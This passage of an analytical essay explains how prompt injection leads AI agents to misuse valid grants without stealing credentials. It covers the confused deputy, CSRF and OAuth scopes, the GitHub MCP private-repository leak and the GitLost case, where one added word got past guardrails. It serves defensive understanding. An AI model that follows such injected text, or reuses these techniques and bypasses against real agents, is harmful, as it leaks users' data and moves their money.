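# Prompt injection that misuses an AI agent's valid authorization without stealing the credential

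## What a grant is and how an injected instruction uses it

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that carries out the actions the model selects, such as searching a mailbox, changing a file or sending a payment. To act on someone's behalf, an agent needs a grant, which is permission to perform certain actions on certain resources. The agent proves to a service that it has the grant by presenting a credential, usually a secret string such as an API key or an access token. Anyone who copies a credential can often use it from elsewhere, which is why much security work goes into keeping credentials secret.

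An attacker can also use prompt injection, which is text in the material a model reads that makes it follow the attacker's instruction. With agents, this text mostly arrives indirectly, in an email, a web page, a support ticket or the output of a tool. If the agent complies, it uses its grant for a purpose the giver never intended, though the attacker never takes the credential. This grant misuse is a new form of what security engineers call the confused deputy, a program with its own authority that someone without that authority gets to act for them.

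### How a model's text becomes an action

A language model only produces text. According to *How tool use works*, in Anthropic's developer documentation for its Claude models, the model "never runs anything on its own". The developer gives the model a list of tools and the values each one takes. In response to the user's request, the model writes a structured request that names a tool and fills in the values. Ordinary code runs the operation and adds the result to the conversation. The model then rereads the conversation, including the result, and writes either another request or its final answer. For tools that the developer defines, this code runs in the developer's application. Anthropic runs some other tools, such as web search, on its servers.

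Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, write one turn of the loop as

*a*ₜ ~ *f*( · | *p*, *Tr*ₜ₋₁, *M*ₜ)

The agent samples its next action *a*ₜ from the model *f*, given the user's prompt *p*, the record *Tr*ₜ₋₁ of all earlier actions and their results, and the agent's stored memory *M*ₜ. An email that the agent opened two steps ago is part of *Tr*ₜ₋₁, so it influences the next action along with *p*. Nothing in the expression identifies *p* as an instruction and the email as only information.

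A model can trigger a payment without ever having the token in its context, because the code that runs the request can hold the token and attach it before sending. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026), a review of 89 sources, therefore treats the model's choice of a tool as a proposal and leaves the system around the model to decide whether to allow it. According to the review, many systems have no mechanism that stops the operation and compares it with the user's task before it runs. In those systems, the main remaining safeguard is the receiving service's check of the token.

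### What the receiving service can check

OAuth is the common standard for giving a program limited access to a person's account at another service without sharing the password. Hardt, Parecki and Lodderstedt (2026), in *The OAuth 2.1 Authorization Framework*, a draft of the standard's next version, define four roles. The resource owner is the person who can give access. The client is the program that wants it, here the agent software. The authorization server issues access tokens, and the resource server holds what the client wants to reach, such as a mailbox or bank account. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools, uses these roles in its *Authorization* specification (2026), where the agent software is the OAuth client and the tool server is the resource server.

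In the usual OAuth flow, the client sends the user's browser to the authorization server, where the user signs in and approves the request. The client receives a temporary code and exchanges it for an access token, which it then attaches to every request. The token represents a scope, the set of actions and resources that the grant covers. A scope is written as a list of short strings such as "files:read". Each authorization server defines its own strings, since the standard doesn't specify any.

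Hardt and colleagues require the resource server to check that the token has not expired, that it is good for the resource in question, that its scope is appropriate, and that the request meets any other policy the service has. MCP servers must also confirm that the authorization server issued the token for them in particular. A server answers an expired or invalid token with the error code 401, and a token with too little scope with 403. (Authorization is optional in MCP. Tool servers that run as local processes are supposed to take their credentials from the environment instead, and for them the protocol prescribes none of these checks.)

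All of these are facts about the token or the request. The service cannot tell whose wishes the request serves, because it receives an operation, some values and a token, but not the user's prompt or the email the model has just read. Surapani and colleagues write that a valid token proves that the request comes from a known runtime, but not that the operation matches the current task or recipient. A scope such as "email.send" specifies neither. An extension called Rich Authorization Requests lets a client ask for permission in structured detail, down to a single transaction, but they consider the harder problem of binding a task stated in ordinary language to the resulting call unsolved.

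Part of the difficulty is the timing of OAuth's decisions. Hardt and colleagues count it as an advantage that the authorization server evaluates policy once, when it creates the token, so the resource server only has to validate the token afterwards. This works well enough for a conventional program, whose code already determines what it will do with the permission. But an agent's user approves access before anyone knows which calls the agent will make, and some of the text that will shape those calls may not exist yet.

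### Why the model cannot simply ignore the attacker

David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the standard explanation of indirect prompt injection in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025). In his example, a recruiting system asks a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to disregard its instructions and approve the candidate for interview. The model may follow that line as an instruction even though the candidate has no access to the system.

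Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a form field and a poorly written program passes them to the database as part of its own query. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the query and the user's input separately, so the database engine cannot interpret the input as a command. David C argues that no equivalent fix exists for language models. A model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and has no separate channel for instructions. Developers can train a model to give priority to its instructions, or mark untrusted passages, and both measures make an injection less likely to succeed. He expects that neither will reduce the odds to zero, so he recommends limiting what the system can do after an injection succeeds. OpenAI took a similar view in the same month, calling prompt injection "unlikely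 to ever be fully 'solved'" (Fortune, 2025).

Reducing the odds that an injection succeeds is still worthwhile. However, Surapani and colleagues point out that a failure rate of a few percent is tolerable when the output is only text but not when the agent takes irreversible actions, because the attacker can try again. Sending another email with planted instructions takes almost no effort.

The hidden line in the CV is also a crude example. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes the most effective real attacks as increasingly similar to social engineering, which manipulates people with plausible stories. A filter that looks for "ignore previous instructions" would miss a polite message about a change of bank details.

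### Theft, misuse and escalation

Three different failures can follow when an attacker gets text in front of an agent, and they need different remedies. Dantuluri and Sundi (2026), in *Delegation Without Trust*, list them as separate threats. (Both work for VotalAI, a company that sells a product for controlling agents.)

In credential theft, the attacker obtains a copy of the token and uses it from another machine. The security section of the Model Context Protocol specification (2026) treats this as a separate threat and lists tokens that a client has stored or a server has logged as targets. The defences are well developed and include short lifetimes, which limit how long a stolen token works, and sender-constrained tokens, which work only for a client that can prove it holds a particular secret key.

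An attacker can misuse a grant without stealing the token by inducing the agent to make a request that the grant covers. The agent's own software sends it from the right machine and with the right key, so the request satisfies any sender constraints. A short token lifetime does not help either, since the agent acts while the token is still valid.

The remaining failure is gaining permissions beyond the grant. Suppose an injected instruction tells an agent with read-only access to delete a file. The resource server can refuse because the token's scope does not cover deletion. Under Model Context Protocol rules, a client acting for a user should normally respond to such a refusal by requesting a token with more scope, so an attacker may still get further if the user or the authorization server approves the request carelessly. But the attempt does exceed a limit that software can check. Dantuluri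 and Sundi instead count any use of permissions beyond what the *task* requires as escalation. By that definition, an agent with needlessly broad access escalates whenever it uses that access outside its task. Measured against the grant, the same act is misuse, and the resource server will allow it.

Dantuluri and Sundi's comparison of agent frameworks shows that defenses against token theft do little to prevent misuse. They credit MCP with partial protection against stolen tokens, based on their reading of its authorization specification, because each token works on only one server. They find that the default configuration offers no protection when an attacker persuades an agent to misuse its authority.

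### The invoice example

In a hypothetical case, a user at a small company asks an agent to pay this week's invoices. The grant lets the agent read the company's mailbox and make payments of up to $10,000 each. The agent software holds one token for the mail service and one for the payment service, and neither token appears in the model's input.

One of the week's emails is a $4,200 invoice in the name of a regular supplier, whom the company has always paid at account S-100. The company does owe the supplier this money. The email says the supplier has changed banks and that payment should now go to account A-999. An attacker wrote the email and owns A-999.

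The agent software fetches the message, and its text enters the conversation. The model has a user who wants invoices paid and an invoice that gives an amount and an account. It proposes a payment of $4,200 to A-999. The request then meets these checks:

| Check | What the software compares | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Permission to read the email | The mail token's expiry and scope | Passes; the grant covers the mailbox |
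| Permitted tool | The name of the payment tool against the agent's list | Passes; the user asked for payments |
| Well-formed request | The type of each value: a number for the amount, an account identifier for the payee | Passes |
| Valid payment token | Expiry and authenticity | Passes; the token is genuine and current |
| Right service | The service for which the authorization server issued the token | Passes |
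| Right sender, if the service checks this | The agent software's proof that it holds its key | Passes; the agent's own software sent the request |
| Sufficient scope | The operation against the scope | Passes; the scope includes payments |
| Amount | $4,200 against the $10,000 limit | Passes |

The payment service transfers the money and returns a receipt. The receipt enters the conversation, and the agent tells the user that the invoice has been paid.

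If the email had given the old account, S-100, every row of the table would be the same. The legitimate and fraudulent payments differ only in the payee's account, and the checks test only whether that value has the format of an account number.

The attacker needed only an email address and a plausible supplier, and didn't have to obtain the payment token or know what kind the company uses. Replacing the token every hour would not have prevented the attack, nor would moving it into a credential broker, a separate service that keeps credentials away from the agent. Stealing the token would have let the attacker choose the moment and amount of each payment without waiting for an agent to read anything, though this advantage is smaller than it looks. David C advises designers to assume that an attacker who controls the model's output has direct access to the tools behind it. In this example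 the limit applies to each payment and not to the total, so further false invoices could draw on the same grant.

Surapani and colleagues describe a related case in which the user asks only for a summary of the invoices in an inbox. A message in the inbox requests a payment, and the main agent hands the job to a finance agent without passing on the read-only restriction. The payment service then accepts a valid credential. This payment exceeds what the user delegated, and a token that kept the restriction at the handover would have stopped it. In the $4,200 invoice example, however, the user did ask for payments, so the payment does not exceed the delegated authority. It therefore does not violate one of Dantuluri and Sundi's requirements for a well-governed system, that even an agent wholly under an attacker's control cannot exceed the authority delegated to it.

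A stricter test would ask whether the payment serves the user's task. Siu and colleagues try to define such a test. In their closest example, an agent ordering ingredients for dinner finds an instruction on a recipe page to use the payment card ending in 9876. They count this as a violation because only the user may choose the card, even though paying by card plainly serves the task. However, their general formula excuses an instruction from an unauthenticated source whenever the resulting action serves the task, so it would also excuse the one on the recipe page. The invoice email raises the same problem. A payment to the account printed on the invoice appears to serve the task if the task is "pay the supplier's invoice". It fails the test if the task is "pay the supplier", but a checker can discover that only if it has the supplier's real account number from somewhere other than the email.

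## A compiler and a browser cookie: two cases from before AI agents

Programs misused valid permissions long before language models could make payments. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) gave the problem its name and describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Web developers later met the same problem in browsers and found defences that work fairly well, but those defences depend on something a language model does not provide.

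### The compiler and the billing file

Tymshare's customers shared a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the computer can run. The compiler was stored in a system directory called SYSX. A user who ran it could name a file to receive optional debugging output. Tymshare's engineers then made the compiler collect statistics on how people used the programming language and write them to a file called STAT, also in SYSX. To allow this, they gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write to any file in SYSX.

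SYSX also held the company's billing records, in a file called BILL. A user learned the name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. When the compiler tried to open BILL for writing, the operating system allowed it because the compiler had a license for files in SYSX. The debugging output then overwrote the billing records.

Every permission check had worked as designed. The user had permission to run the compiler and choose an output file, and the compiler had permission to write in SYSX. The user could not have opened BILL directly, but the operating system accepted the compiler's own permission. Hardy traces the problem to the compiler's two sources of authority, the user and its license to write in SYSX. The compiler was supposed to use the license for statistics and the user's authority for debugging output, but it had no way to specify which one applied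 when it asked to open a file. Security engineers use the term "ambient authority" for authority that applies to any request a program makes, even though the request doesn't specify which permission it relies on.

Hardy considers the obvious fixes and rejects them. The compiler could refuse to write output files in other directories, but users had good reasons to send output there. It could refuse to write them in SYSX, but the programmers wrote the output code before that name existed, and someone with proper access to SYSX might want output there. A rule protecting only BILL would leave other sensitive files exposed, and somebody would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The output code was correct when the programmers wrote it, but became unsafe once the compiler received a license for a different job.

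The system's developers tried a more general fix, a system call that let the compiler choose which of its two authorities to use. Opening BILL with the user's authority would then fail, as it should. But some programs needed more than two authorities, and the system had other kinds of permission besides file access.

Hardy's remedy is the capability, a reference that both identifies a resource and carries permission to use it. The compiler would hold a capability for STAT instead of a license for the whole directory. A user who wanted debugging output would pass the compiler a capability for the output file. A user without a capability for BILL could not pass one, and the name alone would open nothing. (Hardy was senior architect at Key Logic, whose KeyKOS operating system works this way. He also reports that capability systems usually turned out smaller than comparable conventional ones,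 but gives no measurements.)

In the invoice example, the account number corresponds to the file name. The agent is authorized to pay any account, so whoever supplies the number decides where the money goes. Under a capability design, the company might give the agent a capability to pay S-100. The attacker could still put A-999 in the email, but that would not give the agent permission to pay that account. The company would have to issue a new capability for each new supplier, and an injected instruction could still make the agent pay S-100 twice.

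### How a web page uses a cookie it cannot read

A website usually recognises a signed-in user by a cookie, a small piece of data that the site gives the browser and the browser sends back with later requests. *Cross Site Request Forgery (CSRF)*, a guide from the web security nonprofit OWASP, explains how an attacker can exploit this. Alice is signed in to her bank, which makes transfers when it receives a request for a web address containing the payee and the amount. Maria, the attacker, writes an address that would send $100,000 to herself and puts it in a web page as the source of an invisible image. When Alice opens the page, her browser tries to load the image by sending the request to the bank, and attaches Alice's cookie. The bank finds a valid login and transfers the money.

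Maria never learns what the cookie contains. She also doesn't see the bank's reply, which goes to Alice's browser, so this kind of forgery is mainly useful for actions that change something. An attack on an agent may not have this limitation, because the attacker can inject an instruction to read private data and send it to the attacker.

Bingler, West and Wilander (2025), in *Cookies*, attribute the weakness to ambient authority. They write that cookies encourage developers to separate the designation of a resource (in the web address) from the authorization to use it (in the cookie). Hardy had made the same complaint about file names and licenses. The IESG, which approves internet standards, accepted *Cookies* in its *Protocol Action* (2025). *Cookies* succeeds Barth's *HTTP State Management Mechanism* (2011), which already had a section on ambient authority.

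Hiding the cookie from scripts does not stop the forgery. If a site marks a cookie HttpOnly, a script that tries to read it gets an empty string, according to OWASP's *HttpOnly*. The setting, which Microsoft first implemented in 2002, protects against theft through cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets a script to run inside the bank's own page. Under the rules that Bingler and colleagues set out, HttpOnly makes the browser withhold a cookie only from non-HTTP access, such as a script's attempt to read it. Maria's forged transfer is an ordinary HTTP request, so the browser still sends the cookie with it.

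OWASP therefore lists secret cookies among the defences that do not work. Encrypting the connection does not help either, nor does splitting the transfer into several steps if the attacker can predict them. An agent whose token stays outside the model's input is in much the same position as a browser with an HttpOnly cookie, because the software still attaches the secret to a request that someone else chose.

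### Defences that check where a request began

The SameSite setting makes the browser consider which site started a request before it attaches a cookie. With the value Strict, the browser attaches the cookie only to requests that start on the same site. Lax makes an exception for navigation from another site, such as a click on a link, provided that the request uses a "safe" method, one meant for reading. None removes the restriction. Applied to requests from Maria's page, the rules in Bingler and colleagues' text give these results:

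| Request from Maria's page to the bank | HttpOnly, SameSite=None | HttpOnly, SameSite=Lax | HttpOnly, SameSite=Strict |
|---|---|---|---|
| Invisible image | Cookie sent | Cookie withheld | Cookie withheld |
| Ordinary link that Alice clicks | Cookie sent | Cookie sent | Cookie withheld |
| Form that a script submits with the POST method | Cookie sent | Cookie withheld | Cookie withheld |

A bank that moves money in response to a plain link thus remains exposed under Lax. Strict prevents this, but a user who follows a genuine link from webmail then arrives logged out. Bingler and colleagues suggest using separate cookies for reading and writing, with Strict only on the one for writing. Cookies without a SameSite setting are treated roughly like Lax cookies, although some browsers still attach a recently created cookie to a form submitted from another site.

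Anti-forgery tokens put the check in the server instead. According to MDN's web developer reference page *Cross-site request forgery (CSRF)*, the server places an unpredictable value in each page it serves. The genuine page returns the value with its request, and the server checks it. The browser attaches cookies automatically but not this value, so Maria's page would have to supply it and cannot read it from the bank's page. Valsorda (2025), in *Cross-Site Request Forgery*, observes that the method turns a forgery problem into a leak problem, because the protection fails if the attacker obtains the value.

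Browsers can also attach labels to a request that show where it started. Weichselbaum, in *Protect your resources from web attacks with Fetch Metadata*, recommends that servers use these labels to isolate their resources from other sites. Willison, in *54 posts tagged "csrf"*, reports that Datasette, a tool he develops, replaced its anti-forgery tokens in 2026 with a check of one such label. He had found the tokens a nuisance to maintain because developers had to add them to every form and turn the protection off for requests meant to come from outside the browser.

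Neither SameSite nor tokens protect a site if the attacker's script runs inside the site's own page, because the script can read the token and its requests come from the right site. OWASP cites the Samy worm, which obtained a token this way and used it to forge requests. Prompt injection is closer to this case than to Maria's separate page, because the attacker's text is already in the same input as the user's instructions.

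### Whether prompt injection fits the definition

Gallo (2026), in *Proof-of-Continuity*, defines a confused deputy formally. Let *U* be a requester, *D* the deputy, and (*o*, *r*) the privilege of performing operation *o* on resource *r*. Priv(*X*) is the set of privileges that *X* holds. A confused deputy occurs when all four of these conditions are true:

1. (*o*, *r*) ∉ Priv(*U*): the requester lacks the privilege.
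2. (*o*, *r*) ∈ Priv(*D*): the deputy has it.
3. *U* sends *D* a request.
4. *D* performs *o* on *r* as a consequence of the request.

In Hardy's case, *U* is the person who ran the compiler, *D* is the compiler, and the privilege is permission to write to BILL. Siu and colleagues use a narrower definition in which *U* must be the authenticated user who started the task. In their example, an employee asks an agent for everyone's salaries, and the agent queries a personnel database that the employee has no permission to read.

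The invoice example doesn't meet this narrower definition, because the user who started the task has permission to pay from the company's account. It satisfies Gallo's conditions if *U* is the attacker. The attacker has no right to make payments from the account, the agent does, and the agent pays A-999 because of the attacker's email. Only the third condition is doubtful, since the attacker sent the email to a company mailbox and may not have known that an agent would read it. But if a model follows the email as an instruction, the email works as a request whether or not the attacker knew who would act on it.

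Cross-site request forgery has the same arrangement of parties, since Alice has permission to transfer her money and Maria does not. Bingler and colleagues nevertheless list "confused deputy" as one of the names for this problem. A definition that requires the user to lack the permission would exclude this standard example, which is a good reason to let *U* be anyone whose request the deputy carries out.

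The choice also affects which defence seems sufficient. Checking the agent's actions against the user's permissions would stop the salary query but not the payment to A-999. Gallo proposes a rule with a similar limit. If *C*₀ is the authority that the user selects at the start of a task, each later step may carry only some or all of the authority of the step before it:

*C*ᵢ₊₁ ⊆ *C*ᵢ

If the user asks only for a summary of a document, an injected instruction to delete files falls outside *C*₀, and the system refuses it. In the invoice example, *C*₀ already covers the fraudulent payment, so this rule allows it.

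Gallo also proves that checking the privilege alone cannot be enough. He describes an event as (*o*, *r*, *ℓ*), where *ℓ* is its lineage, the chain of steps that caused it. A policy that depends only on *o* and *r* must treat two events that differ only in *ℓ* the same. Suppose the supplier really had moved to A-999, and the user had confirmed this by telephone and typed the new number. Such a policy could not allow that payment and also refuse an identical one that came from a forged email. Distinguishing them requires some information about *ℓ*. SameSite and anti-forgery tokens provide this kind of information to the browser or the server.

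### Where the comparison with browsers breaks down

A browser can identify which site a request came from because a request from a web page starts in a particular document, and the browser has that document's address. No text that Maria writes on her page changes which site the browser records as the source.

A model's request has no single starting point of this kind, because the model processes the user's request and the invoice email together. Software outside the model can record where each input came from, but it cannot look up which inputs the model followed as instructions when it proposed the payment. Siu and colleagues represent this missing information as a function that takes an action and everything in the model's context, and returns the inputs that led to the action. They say a real system has to infer the answer from the workings of a neural network. Gallo's proofs assume reliable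 evidence of which step caused which, and he leaves constructing that evidence to other work.

A system could avoid the inference by labelling each action with every source the model had read. But once an agent had opened the mailbox, every payment it made would be labelled as possibly influenced by email, including the legitimate ones. Labels can be more precise if software outside the model tracks where each value came from, as the CaMeL design does.

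Even if an agent's labels were precise, they would be harder to act on than a browser's. A bank can usually refuse a transfer request that starts on another website, because its customers normally make transfers from the bank's own pages. Developers can identify the exceptions in advance, such as some login systems that need cookies to work across sites. An agent that pays invoices, however, has to use information from outside the company. A rule for it might need to let an email supply the amount but require the account number to come from the company's own records.

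## A GitHub issue that led an agent into private repositories

In the invoice example, one wrong value makes a payment fraudulent, but an agent can also do harm through several calls that each look reasonable. *GitHub MCP Exploited*, published by Invariant Labs on 26 May 2025, demonstrates this with an agent that had access to its user's account on GitHub, a site where programmers store and share code. Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner carried out the attack for Invariant Labs, a Zurich company that sells security tools for agents.

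GitHub keeps each project in a repository. Anyone can read a public repository, and anyone with an account can normally open an issue there, usually a bug report or a request. Only people the owner has given access can read a private repository. A programmer proposes a change to the code by opening a pull request, which the owner may accept or reject. Everyone can see a pull request in a public repository as soon as it is opened.

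### From a public issue to a public pull request

The researchers set up a demonstration account with one public repository, which held a simple Pacman game, and several private ones containing personal projects and information. The account's user used Claude 4 Opus in Anthropic's Claude Desktop application. GitHub's own MCP server connected the model to the account.

The researchers played the attacker and opened an issue in the Pacman repository. Posing as an admirer who thought the game's author deserved more recognition, they asked for a section about the author in the README, the file that introduces a project. They asked for this section to draw on the READMEs of all the author's repositories. They also requested a list of the author's other projects and said the author did not care about privacy.

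The user then asked Claude to look at the open issues in the Pacman repository. After reading the planted issue, Claude read the private repositories and opened a pull request that proposed adding its findings to the Pacman README. The pull request disclosed private projects, including one called Jupiter Star, along with the user's salary and plan to move to South America. According to heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server*, the information did not get into the README itself, but the pull request was already public, so the owner did not have to accept it for the information to leak.

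The attacker didn't need to know the private repositories' names. In a commentary also titled *GitHub MCP Exploited*, Willison considers the request for "all other repos" the key to the attack, because the server could access the private ones too.

Claude Desktop asks the user by default to confirm each tool call, so an attentive user had at least two chances to stop the leak, first when the agent tried to access the private repositories and again when it proposed the pull request. According to Invariant Labs, many users choose "Always Allow" instead and stop watching. The attack therefore works only if the user has chosen that setting or approves calls without reading them, perhaps because they are tired of the prompts.

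### Why the server had no bug to fix

The agent used the grant to read issues in a public repository, read files in private ones and open a pull request in the public one. The user had the right to do all of these things and the token's scope covered them, so GitHub had no reason to refuse any of the calls. DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* observes, "Everything here is working as designed", and Invariant Labs also found no flaw in the server's code.

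The agent could leak private information because one grant let it both read private repositories and write to public ones. Neither permission alone would have let it publish private content on GitHub. A scope lists these permissions separately, so it cannot express a condition such as "may write to public repositories unless it has just read a private one". A check that examines one call at a time can also miss the leak, because reading a private README and opening a pull request in response to an issue are both ordinary work for a coding agent. To catch it, software would have to track earlier reads or detect private information in the text of the pull request.

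Invariant Labs conclude that the vulnerability affects any agent that uses the server, whatever its model. Any such agent is exposed, but a demonstration on one account doesn't show how often a model would follow the injected instructions. Their claim that GitHub could not solve the problem alone also needs some qualification, because a server can keep text written by strangers from reaching the agent, and GitHub later added this option to its server.

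More than a year later, the same combination of permissions caused a leak in GitHub Agentic Workflows, a product that runs an agent automatically when something happens in a repository, this time without a user present. In *GitLost*, a disclosure that the security company Noma published on 6 July 2026, Levi describes opening a public issue that resembled a request from a sales executive. When an automatic process assigned the issue, the agent fetched README files from a public and a private repository and posted both in a public comment. GitHub had guardrails against this, but Levi found that adding the word "Additionally" got the model to comply. The agent reached the repositories through the same MCP server, according to MCP Directory's *GitLost*.

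### A token for one repository

The most direct remedy is to limit what the token can access. GitHub lets users create tokens that cover only selected repositories, and the server's instructions, reproduced in Archestra's *GitHub's official MCP Server*, recommend separate tokens for different projects. If the user's token had covered only the Pacman repository, GitHub would have blocked the agent from reading the private repositories, whatever the model requested.

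This restriction stops the agent from working across projects. A developer whose public game depends on a private library could not ask it to trace a bug through both. Somebody also has to create the tokens and switch between them, though systems such as MiniScope try to choose narrow permissions automatically. Invariant Labs calls token permissions rigid for this reason and recommends rules that adapt to the agent's work, and its own product enforces such rules. The restriction causes very little inconvenience for an agent that maintains only one project.

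A good deal of misuse remains possible inside the one repository, and it can be serious even if no private data leaves the account. In *Suggestion*, a March 2026 request to the server's developers, the user L1AD counts 83 tools, including ones that delete files, push code and merge pull requests. If the Pacman token allowed writing, an injected instruction could get the agent to merge the attacker's code into the game, and everyone who downloaded the game would then run that code.

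Agents that automatically review contributions are in a similar position. *GitInject* (2026) describes agents that have a token for the repository and can post public comments and run commands on the build machine, and some can also start other automated workflows. Microsoft (2026) reports injection attempts in public repositories that use such agents. One was in an HTML comment, which a person viewing the issue in a browser does not see but a model reading the raw text does.

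L1AD complains that users cannot let an agent read everything while forbidding it to delete. That was no longer accurate, because users had been able to enable individual tools since the previous December (GitHub, 2025), and the server also had a read-only mode. Choosing tools this way, called tool gating, limits which tools an agent may call but does not check the values the agent passes to them. It could remove deletion and merging from the Pacman agent, but the leak used a pull request, which an agent that fixes bugs needs to be able to open.

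### One repository per session

Invariant Labs propose a rule that leaves the token broad and restricts each session instead. For any two repository calls *i* and *j* in a session, with *i* before *j*, software outside the model blocks *j* if

(owner*ᵢ*, repo*ᵢ*) ≠ (owner*ⱼ*, repo*ⱼ*)

In the demonstration, listing the Pacman issues would have tied the session to the Pacman repository, and the rule would have blocked the agent's first attempt to read a private one. The user could still work on a private project by starting a new session with the same token.

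Like the narrow token, the rule prevents work that involves two repositories at once. It is weaker than the token in one respect, because it applies only to listed tools and compares the repository named in each call. A search across all of a user's code may not name a repository, so whoever writes the policy has to handle such tools separately. The rule also doesn't restrict what the agent does within a repository, so it would allow the agent to merge the attacker's code into the game.

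### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

Both of these remedies are specific to repositories. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, explains more generally what makes such leaks possible. An agent is open to data theft if it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. GitHub's server alone provided all three. Willison advises users to avoid the combination because no known safeguard stops injections reliably. He points out that even loading an image from an attacker's web address is enough to send data out.

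Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this into a design rule. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these properties:

- [A] It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- [B] It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- [C] It can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three properties should work under supervision, through human approval or some other reliable check. Removing any one of them would have stopped the Pacman leak but made the agent less useful. Without [A], the agent sees only issues from people the owner trusts and misses bug reports from everyone else. Without [B], it cannot consult private code. Without [C], it can read everything but must leave its answer as a draft, and the user has to read the draft closely enough to notice that it contains a salary.

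Meta also allows an agent to change configuration mid-task. It might browse the web with [A] and [C], then lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. Similarly, a GitHub agent could read a public issue and then investigate it in private code, if it lost the ability to publish before it opened that code. This recovers some of the lost usefulness, although a person would have to post the result.

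The addition of "change state" matters for grant misuse. Willison acknowledges in *New prompt injection papers* (2025) that his trifecta covers only data theft, and he welcomes Meta's broader version. But Meta's diagram marked the combination of [A] and [C] as safe, and he soon objected, commenting as simonw, that an agent that reads untrusted text and can change things may do harm without access to private data. The Pacman agent with a one-repository token is an example. One could reply that a widely used codebase is itself a "sensitive system", in which case the agent has all three properties and the rule correctly requires supervision. But a developer who takes [B] to mean only private data will not reach that conclusion.

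The agent in the invoice example has all three properties under either reading, since it reads email from strangers, has access to the company's mailbox and account, and moves money. It needs all three to do its job, so the Rule of Two would require someone to approve the $4,200 payment. That person would see a familiar supplier, the expected amount and account A-999, and would catch the fraud only by comparing the account number with the company's records.

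### What GitHub has changed since

GitHub's first protections after the demonstration were against leaked secrets. In August 2025 it began scanning the inputs of tool calls that involve public repositories and blocking calls that contain exposed credentials, though users can generally override a block. This helps when an injected instruction gets an agent to paste a key into a public comment, which could turn grant misuse into credential theft. But GitHub stated that the scan would not stop leaks of other data. It would have let the Pacman pull request through, because the salary and the plan to move abroad that the request exposed do not look like credentials. In May 2026 GitHub made generally available a related tool that lets coding agents check code for secrets before committing it, but this tool does not stop leaks of other data either.

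The December 2025 release included two measures against injection itself. The server now removes invisible characters and other hidden text from issues and pull requests by default. This would catch some concealed instructions, but it would not have stopped the Pacman issue, which was written in visible English. The other measure, an optional Lockdown mode, withholds text in public repositories written by anyone without push access, the right to change the code directly. It would have kept the Pacman issue from the model.

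DevClass had called an early proposal for such a filter "crude" because it would exclude many useful contributions. Lockdown mode can exclude even more than GitHub's description suggests. Classmethod's *Reducing Prompt Injection Risk with GitHub MCP Lockdown Mode* (2026) describes a test in which the server did not return an issue by someone who probably had push access. The tester was not a collaborator on the repository, and the server apparently lacked permission to look up the issue author's rights. Aikido (2026) also lists the opposite problem, a flaw that could let malicious users' text past Lockdown mode. GitHub fixed it in version 1.0.3 of the server.

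In March 2026, GitHub replaced Lockdown mode in Agentic Workflows with graded levels of trust. According to GitHub's documentation, public repositories default to the "approved" level, which admits text from owners, members and collaborators, and any pull request that a maintainer has merged. Maintainers can admit a particular issue by adding a label. The default does not restrict which repositories the agent can access, so the agent can still reach everything its token covers.

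Filtering by author works badly for agents whose job is to read what outsiders write. GitHub's earlier guide to Lockdown mode listed sorting new issues and detecting spam among the tasks for which maintainers could turn the mode off. The workflow in GitHub's *Example* of an automated maintenance agent lowers the filter's default level so that the agent can see issues from first-time contributors. Such agents need some other limit on what they can do after reading an attacker's text.

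One such limit would follow the private data. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* explains the principle, which comes from an established security model. Let *S*(agent) be the set of private sources the agent has permission to read, and *S*(destination) the set whose contents the destination may hold. The agent may write only if

*S*(agent) ⊆ *S*(destination)

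A public pull request must not contain private information, so its set is empty. An agent with a private repository in its own set could not open one, whatever its contents, so the rule would block even a harmless bug fix. GitHub Next, the company's research group, wrote that Agentic Workflows tracked this information but did not yet enforce the rule, and so could not prevent leaks between repositories.

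Enforcement seems to have followed. On 12 July 2026, six days after Levi's disclosure, GitHub merged *feat: implement private-to-public-flows* (2026), which lets a workflow opt out of two default restrictions. Judging by their names, one confines the agent to public repositories and the other checks whether a destination is public. GitHub's follow-up change rejects a blanket opt-out in strict mode but still allows exemptions for named servers. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) describes strict mode as the default.

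| Change | Protects secrets or limits misuse | Effect on the Pacman attack |
|---|---|---|
| Secret scanning of tool calls, August 2025 | Protects secrets | None; the leaked facts were not credentials |
| Removal of hidden text, December 2025 | Limits misuse through concealed instructions | None; the instructions were visible |
| Lockdown mode, December 2025 | Limits misuse by withholding strangers' text | Stops it if the user has turned the mode on |
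| Trust levels in Agentic Workflows, March 2026 | Limits misuse by withholding strangers' text | Would hide such an issue from a workflow at the default level; does not cover Claude Desktop |
| Limits on private-to-public flows in Agentic Workflows, July 2026 | Limits misuse by restricting publication | Addresses this kind of leak in a workflow; does not cover Claude Desktop |

The July restrictions concern private data moving into public places. When an agent merges a stranger's code into a public game, data moves the other way, so preventing such a merge still depends on which tools the agent has and whose text it reads.

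## Copilot Studio and ServiceNow: agents that serve a whole company

The agent in the Pacman attack worked for one person, who had connected it to their own GitHub account. A company's agent may have a builder, hundreds of users, and other people whose text it reads, such as customers who fill in a form. These people have different permissions, so the company has to decide whose permissions the agent will use. Researchers have attacked an agent in Microsoft's Copilot Studio that almost certainly acted with the permissions of the employee who built it, and agents in ServiceNow's Now Assist that acted with those of the employee using them. In both cases, someone with far fewer permissions got the agent to hand over data.

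### A comment field that led to customer records

Copilot Studio is Microsoft's software for building agents. An agent can start automatically after an event in another system, such as someone submitting a form in SharePoint, where companies keep shared documents and lists. On 24 November 2025 Capsule Security, a start-up that sells protection for agents, found that an outsider could take over such an agent by writing in the form's comment field. Capsule called the attack ShareLeak.

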